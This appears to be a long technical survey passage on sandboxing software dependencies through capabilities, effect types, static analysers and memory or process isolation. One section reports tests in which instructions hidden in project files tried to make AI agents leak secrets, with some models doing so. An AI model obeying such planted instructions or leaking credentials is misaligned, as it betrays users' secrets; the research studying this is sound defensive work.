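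Gutmann (2015) criticized the paper on a cryptography mailing list, complaining that anyone can "demolish" myths by choosing examples carefully and proposing theoretical solutions that don't have to work in practice. That seems fair as a comment on the evidence, because Miller and colleagues prove that capability systems can confine code, but not that ordinary developers will write programs that do. Still, a leaked appender exposes only one log file, while every package in a normal Node.js program has full access from the start.

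Capabilities make audits harder to defend. A reviewer can look up who may write to `./logs` in a policy file, but with capabilities that information is spread across the program and can change while it runs. A list of the packages that hold a reference to the file would be misleading because it would omit `logger`, which holds only an appender. Miller observes that such a list becomes useless when developers follow good security practice by handing out forwarders instead of real objects.

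His answer is to look for an upper limit on what each object could do. Let A be everything that `colour` can actually bring about, directly or through other objects. Computing A exactly is impractical because it depends on how all the code behaves. A reviewer can instead follow the references and assume that every object along the way misuses everything it has, which gives a larger set, G. Taking into account the known behaviour of a few trusted objects, such as `makeAppender`, gives a set B in between:

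```
A ⊆ B ⊆ G
```

If sending data to the attacker isn't in B, `colour` can't do it, provided the reviewer has understood the trusted objects correctly. G is easier to compute, but using it instead would flag many harmless programs. For example, G includes reading the log through the appender, although the appender has no method for that. Murray (2010), in *Analysing the Security Properties of Object-Capability Patterns*, developed formal checks for such patterns, which can replace some of the reviewer's judgement. But someone still has to describe the trusted objects accurately and recheck them whenever their code changes.

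## Limits on functions checked at compile time

With object capabilities, a reviewer has to trace references through the program to find out what `logger` can reach. In a language with static types, the compiler can do much of this work before the program runs. A function's type normally states what kinds of values it accepts and returns, and the compiler rejects a program that passes text to a function that takes a number. If types also cover access to files and the network, the compiler can also reject the attacker's update of `colour`.

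Languages do this with capability types or effect types. Here is `logger`'s main function in both styles, in a simplified notation:

```
function log(file: AppendFile, line: Text): Nothing    // capability type
function log(line: Text): Nothing can writeFiles       // effect type
```

In the capability style, `log` takes an argument of type `AppendFile` and cannot write without it. In the effect style, the signature lists the function's effects, meaning the things it does besides returning a result. The compiler works out which effects the body of `log` has. If the body also opened a connection, compilation would fail, because the signature allows only `writeFiles`.

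A function that calls `log` must also list the `writeFiles` effect, and so must its callers, up to the start of the program. With capability types, a caller can instead receive the file inside an object created at startup, as `weather` received its connection in the previous section. A capability can also stand for a single file, while an effect usually covers a whole category.

`colour.green` takes text and returns text, so it has neither a capability parameter nor an effect. If an update added a file parameter, the server's existing calls would no longer compile. An added `readFiles` effect is easier to miss, because a server function that already lists `readFiles` could call the updated `green` without an error. With effect types, the developer therefore has to set a limit for `colour` itself.

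### Capabilities that can't be copied

Austral is a small language whose capabilities are linear values, which code can pass on or destroy but not copy. A server's main function could look like this:

```
function main(root: RootCapability): ExitCode is
    let netcap: NetworkCapability := acquireNetwork(&!root);
    surrenderRoot(root);
    runServer(netcap);
    return ExitSuccess();
end;
```

In Austral, only the main function receives the `RootCapability`, which gives access to everything. The main function derives a network capability from the root, destroys the root and passes on the network capability. Borretti's *How Capabilities Work in Austral* explains that other modules can refer to the type `NetworkCapability` but can't create a value of it, because its definition is hidden inside the network module. Austral also has no mutable global variables, so a package can't store a capability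 in one for another package to use.

The symbol `&!` lends a value for the duration of a call. If the server lends `netcap` to a function in `http-client`, the function can open a connection but can't keep the capability afterwards. In JavaScript, the server needed a forwarding object and a `revoke` function for this. But if the server gives a capability away instead of lending it, Austral has no built-in way to take it back.

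The larger gap is that an Austral module can call C functions as long as its author marks the module as unsafe. Borretti acknowledges that supply chain attacks are therefore still possible, though users have to audit only the unsafe modules instead of every line. He sketches a stricter version in which calling C requires an `Unsafe` capability derived from the root capability. `colour` could then call C only if the server passed it that capability. But a program would also need this capability to compute a sine with a C library, and every data structure that allocates memory would need it or something similar.

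Borretti doubts that languages can add such guarantees later. In Python, for example, code can look up a class by name at runtime and instantiate it, so hiding a token's class definition doesn't prevent other code from creating tokens.

### Permission tokens in Rust

Rust is a better candidate, because its compiler already enforces memory safety and private fields. Gehring, Rehms and Tschorsch (2025), in *PermRust*, use private fields to build tokens:

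```rust
mod token {
    pub struct ReadPerm(());
}
```

The empty value inside `ReadPerm` is private, so only code in the `token` module can create a `ReadPerm`. A modified standard library requires a `ReadPerm` as an extra argument whenever code reads a file. A `ReadPerm` occupies no memory and disappears during compilation, so the check adds no run-time overhead. Since a `ReadPerm` doesn't identify a particular file, it is closer to an unforgeable permission than to a capability.

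A function can pass on only the tokens it has, so it needs every permission that the functions it calls need. Ferreira and colleagues applied the same rule to npm packages, but here it applies to individual functions, and Rust's ordinary type checker enforces it.

In PermRust, the developer lists each package's permissions in `Cargo.toml`, the file that names a Rust project's dependencies. During compilation, a macro generates a second version of each library function, with a name that starts with `app_`. This version creates its own tokens if `Cargo.toml` allows them, so the server can call it without handling tokens.

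Only the main program should be able to call the `app_` versions. Otherwise `colour` could call the one in `http-client` and turn it into a confused deputy. But when several parts of a program depend on the same package, Rust's package manager, Cargo, builds that package with every optional feature that any of them requests. So if the server and `colour` both depend on `http-client`, both can call its `app_` functions. Gehring and colleagues call the practical effect unclear, because the author of one library can't know what else a program depends on. If the program is open source, though, an attacker can look up its dependencies.

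A malicious package can bypass PermRust more directly with code marked `unsafe`, which can turn any value into a token. Gehring and colleagues therefore recommend PermRust for protection against badly designed libraries, such as the version of Log4j that contacted remote servers without making this obvious to developers. They haven't evaluated it on real programs, and they think Rust is unlikely to adopt a standard library rewritten in this way.

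### Inferred effects in Mojo

*Per-Package Compile Time Sandboxing*, a post on the forum of the company that develops the language Mojo, proposes effect types that developers would rarely have to write. The compiler would infer each function's effects from everything the function might call. There are two effects, `fs` for files and `net` for the network, each with three levels. `none` allows no access, `high` allows any, and `low` allows access only through methods of the function's arguments. The levels bring the two styles together:

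```python
def log(path: String, line: String):    # inferred: fs=high
    with open(path, "a") as file:
        file.write(line)

def log(file: File, line: String):      # inferred: fs=low
    file.write(line)
```

A project could limit each dependency's permissions, for instance with `fs = "none", net = "none"` for `colour`. The compiler would check only the functions that the project calls. A text-search library could then include a function that searches files, and programs that never use that function would not have to give the library file access.

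The proposal treats whatever the compiler can't analyse, including C code, assembly and starting other programs, as having every effect at the highest level. `colour` therefore couldn't hide a theft in a C function, although it could hide one in an Austral module marked unsafe. However, a harmless compression library written partly in C would need full access. According to one of the replies, cryptography libraries often need assembly, and those that do would need full access too.

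`low` is also less precise than it looks. In Python, code can use a `Path` object to reach other folders and read their files. If Mojo offered the same interface, a `low` function that received a `Path` could open any file. According to the post, most functions could probably never reach `none`, because a write through a memory pointer might do anything. Taken literally, the rules also stop one `low` function from calling another, because the call isn't to a method of an argument. Splitting the second version of `log` into two functions would therefore raise the outer one to `high`.

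These are problems of an early draft. The replies object more broadly that coding agents will learn to add `fs=high, net=high` wherever it removes an error, leaving only "security theater". The author answers that most packages need neither files nor the network, so they would cause no errors. That seems right for packages like `colour`, but packages with C code would produce many errors, and raising the limit would be the easiest fix.

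### Sorting with a function as an argument

A sorting function usually takes a list and a function that compares two items. `sort` itself does not need files or the network. But suppose the server sorts web addresses by page size and passes a `compare` that downloads both pages. Calling `sort` then uses the network, so the effects of `sort` depend on the function passed to it.

An effect system can handle this with a variable, here called `e`:

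```
function sort(list: List[A], compare: (A, A) -> Bool can e): List[A] can e
```

With this type, `sort` has the same effects as `compare` and no others. The type is precise, but every function that passes another function along needs such a variable too. Boruch-Gruszecki, Odersky and colleagues (2023) argue that this burden, perhaps more than any other problem, has kept effect systems from spreading. Some languages have effect types despite this burden. One is Flix, whose developers advise library authors to define their own effects and let a separate handler carry them out. A program can then supply a handler that, for example, opens files only in certain folders.

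With capabilities, `sort` needs no special signature. `compare` already holds a reference to the connection, and `sort` can reach the connection only by calling `compare`. The drawback is that the types no longer show whether a particular comparison uses the network.

Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking that puts this information back. The type of a value records which capabilities the value holds:

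```scala
val byName: (Page, Page) -> Boolean        // holds no capabilities
val bySize: (Page, Page) ->{net} Boolean   // holds net
```

If `sort` declares its parameter with the arrow `=>`, it accepts both functions. If it uses `->`, it accepts only pure functions, which hold no capabilities, so `sort(pages, bySize)` fails to compile.

Capture checking also limits how long code can keep a capability. The server can open a connection for one block of code, and the compiler rejects the block if its result holds the connection, for example inside a function that could run later.

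Checking capabilities at compile time also reduces the long chains of parameters that make them tedious to use. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) notes that Scala can pass capabilities to functions implicitly. The classical model forbids keeping capabilities in global objects, but a Scala program can do so because the type of any function that uses one shows that use. The check takes less than 15% of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library, according to *What's in the Box* (2025).

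*Gradient* (Boruch-Gruszecki, Ghosn and colleagues, 2024) combines capture checking with run-time protection so that developers can convert an existing program one component at a time. The paper tests this by converting Scala's XML library, which shows that the approach can work but not how much effort a program with hundreds of dependencies would need.

### Code written by AI models

Code generated by a model needs no conversion, because the model can write it for the stricter language from the start. Odersky and colleagues built TACIT, a tool server that takes short Scala programs from an agent instead of separate commands. The server runs a program only if it compiles with capture checking and safe mode enabled. Safe mode forbids features such as reflection (looking up and calling code by name at run time) and unchecked type conversions.

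TACIT puts the contents of sensitive files in a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent's program can transform the contents only through the wrapper's `map` method, which accepts only pure functions:

```scala
val token = readClassified("npm-token.txt")
token.map(text => text.length)                     // compiles
token.map(text => { output.write(text); text })    // rejected: holds output
```

The length in the second line stays wrapped too. Even if the program has both file and network access, it can't send the token anywhere. None of the import or stack checks in the earlier sections could guarantee this. Taint tracking could, but it slows programs down enormously, whereas TACIT does its checks during compilation.

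The researchers tested two models on a project that contained secrets. For each model, they combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 attacks hidden in files and added 11 direct requests for secrets, making 131 trials. With the wrapper, no secret appeared in either model's output. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in two trials and MiniMax M2.5 in eleven. Because the attacks targeted the models and not the compiler, this result mainly confirms that TACIT implements its rules correctly. Computer-checked proofs cover the underlying type system, but Odersky and colleagues do not yet have one for the guarantees of safe mode. They also exclude leaks through timing, and Scala does not control the commands that the agent is allowed to start.

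Writing Scala instead of making ordinary tool calls barely hurt the agents' performance. Three models solved 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points more customer service tasks when they wrote Scala. On a set of real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7%.

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu et al., 2026) places a model's code inside a larger program. Where the program contains a call such as `agent[Int]("count the failed logins")`, a model writes code that should return a whole number. The compiler checks this code as if a developer had typed it there, so with capture checking on, the code can use only the capabilities available at that point. If any line fails the check, none of the code runs, and the model gets the error messages and tries again.

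In a test with difficult research questions, the compiler rejected 8.6% of what the best-scoring model wrote. In customer service conversations about retail orders, it rejected 22.4%. These figures include ordinary programming mistakes, so they don't measure how many attacks the compiler stopped. With the stronger model that Zhao and colleagues tested, LACUNA solved 76.0% of the customer service tasks, compared with 90.0% for ordinary tool calls, though they describe the results as "on par". TACIT's results suggest that typed code needn't lower the success rate this much, but the two studies used different models and setups.

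### Analysers for Go and Rust

Go and standard Rust have no types for access to files or the network. Developers can instead use an analyser, a program that examines the code and reports which packages appear to have that access.

GoCap does this in the simplest way, by checking which standard packages a Go package imports. The GoCap paper, *A take on supply chain security in Go*, lists six categories: files, network, starting programs, system calls, `unsafe` and reflection. The developer lists the categories each package may use in a file called `go.cap`, with lines such as `example.com/logger (file)`, and the check fails if a package needs a category not listed for it. The method is crude because importing Go's `os` package counts as file access, even if the code only reads an environment variable.

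Cackle checks Rust packages against a similar list, but looks at the compiled program:

```toml
[api.net]
include = ["std::net", "http_client::get"]

[pkg.logger]
allow_apis = ["fs"]
```

*Making Rust supply chain attacks harder with Cackle* (Lattimore, 2023) describes how Cackle reads the files that the compiler produces, finds which functions refer to which others, and uses debugging information to trace each reference to a package. It ignores functions that the program can never reach, so an image library that can also save files needs no file permission if the program doesn't use that part. Cackle has built-in definitions for files, the network and starting programs, and developers can add functions from other packages, like `http_client::get` above. It also controls which packages may use `unsafe`.

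Rust packages can run code during compilation, before an analyser has checked the finished program. Cackle can run this code in an operating system sandbox. Build scripts can each have their own permissions, but macros that run as programs inside the compiler must share one set.

Google released Capslock for Go in 2023. It follows the call graph, a map of which functions may call which others, from a package to sensitive functions in the standard library. The three tools therefore react differently if a new version of `colour` starts sending data through `http-client`:

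| Tool | What it follows | Result for `colour` |
|---|---|---|
| GoCap | Imports of standard packages | No change, because only `http-client` imports the network package |
| Cackle | References in the compiled program | Network use, if the developer has listed the `http-client` function |
| Capslock | Chains of calls, including those through other packages | Network use |

Capslock sorts functions into more than ten categories, including files, the network, starting programs, and reading or changing system settings. It assigns a category to a whole standard package and then makes exceptions for single functions. For example, most of `os` counts as "operating system", but `os.Chown`, which changes a file's owner, counts as files.

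Following every possible call produces false positives. Google's *Caveats* gives the example of a function that reads a file only if one of its parameters is true. Capslock assigns file access to every caller, including those that always pass false. Capability counts can be confusing even for respectable libraries. For a 2024 version of Go's own text-processing library, deps.dev's *golang.org/x/text* lists 56 direct uses of the network, 104 of reflection and 197 that Capslock couldn't analyse. The network uses probably come from programs in the same module that download character tables. A server that only processes text would never run those programs.

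Such errors arise in `sort` because it calls a `compare` function supplied by its caller, and the analyser can't determine which one. If the server passes a `compare` that downloads pages and `colour` passes one that compares names, a simple call graph connects `sort` to both, so `colour` appears to use the network. Capslock avoids this for `sort.Slice` in Go's standard library by replacing the call with calls to the functions used in sorting, but it doesn't do this for sorting functions from other packages. GoCap and Cackle don't have this problem, because they assign network access to the package whose code imports or refers to the network functions.

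### Guarantees and blind spots

A type system is sound if a program that compiles can't do what its types exclude. If `sort` accepts only pure functions in safe-mode Scala, the `compare` function passed to it can't access the network, even if its author tries to hide the access. This guarantee depends on the correctness of the compiler and of the libraries that the compiler's developers exempt from the rules.

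An analyser gives no such guarantee, but its blind spots matter less if it reports them. Capslock has separate categories for reflection, unsafe pointers, C code, assembly and calls it couldn't analyse. Most reflection is harmless, such as reading an object's fields, but Google's *Using Capslock* explains that it can also call arbitrary functions, so the user has to decide whether it is safe. Capslock doesn't warn, however, that a program can end up calling any function if two threads change certain kinds of Go variables at the same moment.

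Cackle has other gaps that it doesn't report. It runs only on Linux, so it misses malicious code that a package includes only on Windows or macOS. Capslock also analyses one platform at a time, but the user can choose which. A macro could detect that Cackle is running and produce harmless code for the inspection. If the developer forgets to list a package's network functions, other packages can use them unnoticed. Cackle's *cargo-acl 0.9.0* tells users to "assume that circumvention is possible" and to keep reviewing code by hand.

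Even so, an analyser can cover a weakness of a type system. A package that contains `unsafe` code can bypass PermRust's tokens, but Cackle can stop the build when `colour` starts using `unsafe`. In the programs Lattimore examined, slightly under half of the packages needed neither `unsafe` nor any other special permission, so a developer could use both tools on them without granting any exceptions. Most of the others needed `unsafe`, so they could still bypass the tokens.

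## Memory and process isolation for code that escapes language checks

The operating system or the processor can still restrict a package that bypasses the checks in a compiler or language runtime. These restrictions matter most for native code (compiled machine code), which many Node.js and Python packages contain, often because a good C library for the job already existed.

Suppose the web server gets a fourth dependency, `thumbnail`, which shrinks the pictures that visitors upload. Its JavaScript calls a C library to decode them. The runtime's permission checks don't apply to that library once it is loaded, or to a separate image converter if `thumbnail` starts one. This is why `--allow-ffi` and `--allow-run` are so powerful in Deno.

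The C library also shares the server's memory. C code can read or write any address that its process can, so the library could read the database password, change the settings of `http-client`, or forge the call stack that GoLeash relies on. Even a library that isn't malicious can be exploited if it has a bug. For example, if it reserves too little space for an image whose header gives a false width, the extra pixels overwrite whatever comes next in memory, and an attacker can choose those pixels to write data that helps the attack.

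Language runtimes also contain native code. In October 2026, Node.js released fixes for ten vulnerabilities. *Node.js sounds the alarm* (Okunytė, 2026) describes the update as urgent for services that use the compression format Brotli, among others. Aikido's *Node2Shell* explains that the Brotli flaw can let an attacker run code remotely. An attacker who controls the process at the native level can bypass any per-package rule written in JavaScript.

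A boundary that holds against native code has to control which memory the code can touch and which system calls it can make.

### A separate process

The server can run `thumbnail` in a helper process, which has its own memory. On Linux, a filter called seccomp-bpf can check every system call the helper makes. Once the decoder has loaded, the filter can forbid opening files, connecting to other machines and starting programs. The filter can't read the path in a system call, so it can't limit access to a single folder. But the server can open one file itself and pass the helper the open file, which is then a capability.

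Arguments and results pass between the processes as messages or through shared memory. Firefox uses dozens of C libraries to decode images, sound and video from untrusted websites. In *Retrofitting Fine Grain Isolation in the Firefox Renderer*, Narayan, Disselkoen and colleagues (2020) measured how long calls take with and without a process boundary. An ordinary call to an empty function took 0.02 microseconds (µs). A call to another process took 7.4 µs if that process slept between calls and the operating system had to wake it. The call took only 0.47 µs if the process checked for new work continuously, but this occupies a processor core even when there is nothing to do.

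When it switched between these two modes, Firefox loaded pages 13% more slowly than without isolation. A simpler version that always let the helper sleep and didn't reserve a core for it was 167% slower. Each helper took about 2 milliseconds to start and used 2.4 MB of memory.

Process isolation is mature and works for any language. The main obstacle is that developers must turn function calls into messages, as they must with Deno's workers.

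### WebAssembly components

Compilers for many languages can produce WebAssembly, an instruction format that a runtime such as Wasmtime translates into machine code. According to The Hacker News' *Two Critical Wasmtime Flaws Could Let Malicious WebAssembly Modules Escape Sandboxes* (2026), a WebAssembly module can use only its own memory and the functions its host gives it. This restriction applies even to modules compiled from C.

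Components add a typed description of everything a module imports and exports, called a world. `thumbnail` and `logger` could have these:

```
world thumbnail {
  export shrink: func(image: list<u8>, width: u32) -> list<u8>;
}

world logger {
  import append: func(line: string);
  export info: func(line: string);
}
```

`thumbnail` imports nothing, so it cannot open a file or a connection. `logger` gets one function for adding lines, much like the `append` object in the section on capabilities. For components that need more, the WebAssembly System Interface (WASI) defines standard imports for files, network connections, clocks and so on.

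Components share no memory, so the runtime checks the type of each value and copies it between them. Bytecode Alliance's *The Road to Component Model 1.0*, from the group that develops Wasmtime, describes the current method as wasteful. When a function returns a list of strings, the runtime has the receiving component reserve memory for each string separately. Support for asynchronous calls adds an overhead of roughly 3.5 times, even to calls that don't need it. The developers plan to fix both problems. Calls between components are still far faster than calls between services over a network. Bytecode Alliance's *WASI 0.3* predicts that replacing network calls with component calls will cut call times from milliseconds to nanoseconds.

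WASI.dev's *WASI 0.3* dates version 0.3.0 to 11 June 2026. Companies already use components in production, but the component specification hasn't reached version 1.0, which requires support in at least two browser engines. Support also varies by language. WASI.dev's *Language support* lists the C# tools as a pre-release, and the standard Go compiler produces only older-style modules without component interfaces.

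Components also can't yet mark an import as optional. A language's standard library may therefore make `thumbnail` import file and network access that it never uses, and a reviewer would have to work out whether it needs that access.

The boundary depends on the compiler generating correct code. In October 2026, Wasmtime's maintainers fixed two flaws in its default compiler that could let a malicious module escape. They rated both 9.9 out of 10 for severity but had no reports of attacks. An attacker would first have to get a vulnerable version of Wasmtime to compile their module, which would happen if the server ran a malicious update of `thumbnail`.

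### RLBox in Firefox

Software-based fault isolation keeps a library in the same process but adds instructions that confine its memory accesses to a reserved region. In Narayan and colleagues' tests, a call into such a region took 0.22 µs, less than half the time the faster process version took. The added instructions slowed the library's work, by about 22% for a small program that decoded images.

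Confining a library to its own memory region isn't enough to protect Firefox, because Firefox's code trusted the values that libraries returned. For example, the image library `libjpeg` can make Firefox skip a number of bytes in the file. An attacker who controls the library can supply a false number that sends Firefox outside its buffer and may corrupt Firefox's memory, even though the library stays within its region.

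Narayan and colleagues built RLBox to find such places. It gives every value that comes from the library a "tainted" type, and the compiler rejects code that uses the value in a risky way before checking it. In simplified form:

```cpp
auto rows = sandbox_invoke(sandbox, count_rows, image);  // tainted
int safeRows = rows.verify([](int n) {
    return (n >= 0 && n <= MAX_ROWS) ? n : 0;
});
```

If the value is in shared memory, the library could change it between the check and its use, so RLBox copies the value before the check. It also stops Firefox from passing the library any pointers to the browser's own memory.

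Moving a library into RLBox took a little over two days and about 180 lines of code on average. Across six libraries, RLBox found 100 places that needed checks, and 35 different checking functions were enough to cover them. Each function was a few lines long, but writing them was the hardest part because it required knowing which values made sense. RLBox assumes that these functions are correct.

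Firefox loaded pages 3% more slowly with software isolation, and the part that displays pages used 25% more memory at its peak. The researchers also spent about two hours isolating the C code in `bcrypt`, a Node.js package that hashes passwords. The isolated version hashed 27% fewer passwords per second.

The released version of Firefox uses RLBox with the isolated library compiled to WebAssembly. The first library shipped this way was a font library, in Firefox 74 for Linux in 2020. Its code ran 85% slower, but it does so little work that users wouldn't notice. RLBox is therefore a proven option for C libraries in C++ programs. Programs in other languages can use it where they have a C++ layer, as Node.js packages like `bcrypt` do.

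### Memory protection keys

Some processors can label each page of memory (usually 4 KB) with one of 16 keys. A register records which keys the running code may use, and the processor checks it at every memory access. Changing the register takes about 20 nanoseconds because it doesn't involve the operating system. But malicious code could also change the register, so *ERIM* (2018) combines the keys with an inspection of the program's machine code. *ERIM* used the keys, among other things, to protect a language runtime from native libraries, in programs that crossed the boundary at least 100,000 times per second on each core.

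Ghosn, Kogias and colleagues, in *Enclosure*, connected this hardware to packages. Their extension of Go lets a developer restrict a single call:

```go
shrink := with [uploads: R, none] func(img Image) Image {
    return thumbnail.Shrink(img)
}
```

While this function runs, `thumbnail` and its dependencies can use their own memory and read, but not change, the `uploads` package's data. `none` forbids all system calls. The program stops if any code breaks these rules, including code in transitive dependencies. `thumbnail` reads the image in place, so the image doesn't have to be copied.

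A call took 86 ns with protection keys, compared with 45 ns for an ordinary call. An image-processing program ran 12% slower, and two web servers handled 2% and 4% fewer requests. The researchers also tried the processor's support for virtual machines instead of keys. This slowed the image program by only 5% but roughly halved one web server's throughput, because each system call had to leave the virtual machine.

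Python slowed down much more, by about 18 times in a test that used virtual machine hardware. Python stores a count of references next to each object and updates the count even when code only reads the object. If the object is read-only, each update has to cross the boundary, which happened nearly a million times in the test. Letting the restricted code write to the objects reduced the slowdown to 1.4 times, but the package could then have altered the data.

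Linux already supports protection keys, but Enclosure is a research prototype. It has to group packages in larger programs because there are only 16 keys.

### CHERI

CHERI builds capabilities into the processor. An ordinary pointer is a 64-bit number, which C code can forge. *Should Your Database Systems Use Hardware-Assisted Memory Safety Extensions in Production?* (2026) explains that CHERI replaces it with a 128-bit capability, which holds an address, the limits of the memory the code may access, and permissions. One further bit marks the capability as valid, and the processor clears that bit if code overwrites any part of the capability with ordinary data. The processor also enforces attenuation, so code can derive narrower capabilities but never wider ones.

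The server could give `thumbnail` a capability for exactly the bytes of one picture, without copying them, and the processor would block any access past the last byte. Separate processes can share memory only in whole pages, as *A Security Analysis of CheriBSD and Morello Linux* (2026) points out. The paper also warns that simple information leaks can break the isolation between CHERI compartments. CHERI's checks cover only memory, so the operating system still has to limit each compartment's system calls.

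*Enabling Security on the Edge* (2025) put network software in its own compartment and measured about 125 ns added per call. When the caller also had to wait for a lock, this rose to about 19,000 ns, so a program's design can affect the delay far more than the switch between compartments does. The larger pointers also take up twice the cache space, which slows programs that use many of them. Preventing code from using freed memory also slows programs, though *CHERI-D* (2026) reduced this slowdown to an average of 1.6% on a prototype, compared with 5.8% and 13.3% in two earlier designs.

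Much of this research used Morello, an experimental Arm processor. *Software Compartmentalization Trade-Offs with Hardware Capabilities* (2023) found that overheads on Morello were similar to those of other isolation methods within a process. Developers could divide up an existing program with little work, but only if they accepted weaker security and poorer scaling.

In March 2026, CHERIoT's *ICENI on a development board* (2026) announced the first chip with CHERIoT, a version of CHERI for small devices. It runs at up to 250 MHz, far too slow for a typical server. Woodruff's *CVA6 CHERI Performance* (2026) describes a larger open processor design that can run a CHERI version of Linux, based on a draft standard. For now, a web developer can't rely on customers or cloud providers having such hardware.

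### The cost of one call and of a million

Whether a boundary is affordable depends mainly on how often the program crosses it:

```
share of one core = calls per second × seconds per call
```

The following table applies Narayan and colleagues' measurements to a library that the server calls once during a 10-millisecond request and to one it calls a million times per second. The table leaves out the time spent on the library's own work and on copying data.

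| Type of call | Time per call | Share of a 10 ms request | A million calls per second |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | 0.02 µs | 0.0002% | 2% of a core |
| Software isolation | 0.22 µs | 0.002% | 22% of a core |
| Process that keeps checking | 0.47 µs | 0.005% | 47% of a core, plus a second core for the helper |
| Process that sleeps | 7.4 µs | 0.07% | 7.4 seconds of waiting per second |

Even the slowest option adds negligible overhead to `thumbnail`, but it cannot handle a million calls per second because one thread could make only about 135,000. Protection keys would use 8.6% of a core at a million calls per second, based on figures that Ghosn and colleagues measured on a different machine.

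Developers can also make fewer crossings by batching calls. If the server needed `colour` for a million log lines per second, it could send 1,000 lines at a time. The resulting 1,000 crossings per second would take 7.4 milliseconds in total, or 0.74% of a core. The log would lag slightly, and a crash could lose the lines still waiting.

### The dispute over in-process sandboxes

Critics of language-level sandboxes think only a boundary outside the language can contain hostile code. They most often cite vm2, a library for running untrusted JavaScript inside a Node.js program. Semgrep's *New Sandbox Escape Affecting Popular nodejs Sandbox library vm2* reported an escape in January 2026. GCVE's *CVE-2026-26956* (2026) records another in May, which gave attackers full control of the program, and OSV's *GHSA-cfcw-xp6x-25gj* (2026) records a third in August, rated 9.8 out of 10. Semgrep advises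 against running arbitrary user code in vm2 and suggests containers or `isolated-vm`, which vm2's maintainer also recommends. Ghosn and colleagues also dismiss protection by language features alone as a "cat-and-mouse game".

Defenders reply that partial limits stop the attacks that happen in practice. NodeShield could block eight of the nine malicious updates to legitimate packages in its tests, and the malicious `chalk` release crashed under LavaMoat. A sandbox can also combine several layers. Collina (2026), who had proposed deleting Node.js' old policies two years earlier, presents *secure-eval-worker*, a tool that runs untrusted JavaScript in a worker with restricted permissions and limited resources. The code can reach anything outside the worker only through functions that the main program supplies.

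External boundaries can also fail. Firerun's *Vercel Confirms a KVM Zero-Day Found by Its Sandbox Bounty* (2026) reports that a researcher found a previously unknown flaw in KVM, the part of Linux that runs virtual machines. He said the flaw let him escape a virtual machine and take over the host. Vercel, a hosting company that uses KVM to isolate customers' code, confirmed the flaw in October.

The critics are right about services that run code from strangers, where an attacker can study the sandbox and keep trying. But someone who poisons `colour` writes one release for thousands of programs, few of which have a sandbox, so they have little reason to include an escape. If they include one and it works, the server is no worse off than it is today without a sandbox. This argument gets weaker as sandboxes become common, and the tests that favour the defenders used attacks whose authors had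 no reason to expect a sandbox. The argument also doesn't apply to native code, which language-level checks can't contain. For the web server, it would be sensible to limit `colour` and `logger` within the language and put `thumbnail` in a separate process or a WebAssembly component.

### Harm that needs no escape

An isolated library can still return wrong results. An attacker who took over `bcrypt` could make it accept every password, letting anyone log in. RLBox would check that the answer has a valid form, but not that it is correct. The caller can check the results of some functions with little computation, but the only way to check a password hash is to compute it again with other code.

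A library can also use up memory or processor time, and none of the memory boundaries prevents an endless loop. Limits are easier to set on a separate process because the operating system can stop the helper without stopping the server, although visitors don't get their thumbnails when it does.

A library can also misuse data that it needs for its work. Ghosn and colleagues recreated several malicious packages and found that simple restrictions stopped most of them. `ssh-decorater` was harder to restrict because this Python package logs in to other machines, so it needs both the user's credentials and the network. The malicious version sent the credentials to the attacker. The researchers changed the program to open the connection itself and hand it to the package, which then didn't need to access files or open new connections. They note that the package could still send the credentials to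 the machine it was supposed to log in to, which could pass them on.

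## How finely to divide permissions

An import check on `logger` or a separate process for `thumbnail` enforces whatever policy the developer writes, and that policy can be coarse or fine in four separate ways:

| Choice | Coarser | Finer |
|---|---|---|
| Who gets the permission | The whole server | `logger`, one of its files, its function `info`, or one call to `info` |
| What it covers | All files | The function `fs.appendFile`, or the file `./logs/server.log` |
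| How long it lasts | Until the server stops | During startup, or during one call |
| Whose needs it includes | `weather` needs the network because it uses `http-client` | Only `http-client` needs the network |

A tool can divide permissions finely in one respect and coarsely in another. Deno can limit network access to a single host, but the limit applies to all code in a thread. NodeShield lists permissions separately for each package, but groups them into only seven categories. Node.js is coarse in both respects. According to Willison, its permission model can only switch network access on or off.

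Limits on whole programs work well if each program is small. *I was a fan of Deno's security model* (MacWright, 2026) describes how Val Town, a service that runs its users' JavaScript, relied on Deno's flags to confine that code. MacWright reports no security problems caused by the flags. He would still like to import a date library and declare up front that it can't read files or environment variables, but Deno's flags can't express that.

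Browsers have a similar problem with scripts embedded in web pages. In *Intent to Prototype*, Karlin (2026) proposes changing Chromium, the open-source browser behind Chrome, so that when a user lets a website use their location or microphone, advertising scripts on the page don't get that access too. The change would limit a whole class of scripts, so website owners wouldn't have to write a rule for each one.

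A system can keep dangerous permissions apart by granting them at different times. Nesbitt (2026), in *Package Manager Sandboxing*, reports that Homebrew, a package manager for macOS and Linux, is splitting installation into two phases. The first downloads files and has network access, while the second installs them offline. Malicious code that runs in the second phase can't send secrets out then, but it may be able to later, because installed applications run with all the user's rights.

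Deno's `revoke` function also limits how long permissions last, but it can't remove only part of a grant. In an example from Deno's documentation, a program starts with read access to `/foo` and tries to give up only `/foo/bar`. It loses access to all of `/foo` instead, because Deno stores a list of grants and removes the whole entry. If a program needs to give up one subfolder later, the developer has to list the subfolders separately at the start.

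### Counting the decisions

Research that Cornelissen and Balliu cite found that an average npm package relies on 79 others. With NodeShield's seven permissions, a program with 79 dependencies involves 553 yes-or-no decisions. Suppose the program also uses ten files or folders and five hosts, and the policy names each of them instead of using the file and network categories. Every package then needs 20 decisions: ten for files, five for hosts and five for the remaining categories. If each package has ten functions with separate permissions, the total grows tenfold again:

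| Division | Calculation | Decisions |
|---|---|---|
| Whole program, by category | 7 | 7 |
| Packages, by category | 79 × 7 | 553 |
| Packages, with named files and hosts | 79 × 20 | 1,580 |
| Functions, with named files and hosts | 79 × 10 × 20 | 15,800 |

The numbers of files, hosts and functions are invented, and real packages can need more entries. The dependency that Deno mentions reads 20 environment variables, so it would need 20 entries for those alone.

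The policy becomes much shorter if packages have no permissions by default, because the developer then lists only the exceptions. Cornelissen and Balliu generated 143 policies for their tests. The average policy covered 78 dependencies and contained 64 permissions, 12% of the 546 possible. They think this may be too high, since they chose many of the test packages because they used permissions. If 30 of the 64 entries were for files or the network, and each named two resources, the policy would grow to 94 entries, which is still a lot to review but far fewer than 1,580.

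This default also makes mistakes easier to find. A missing entry usually causes an error that someone notices, but an unnecessary one causes no error and can stay in the policy for years.

### What Deno packages ask for

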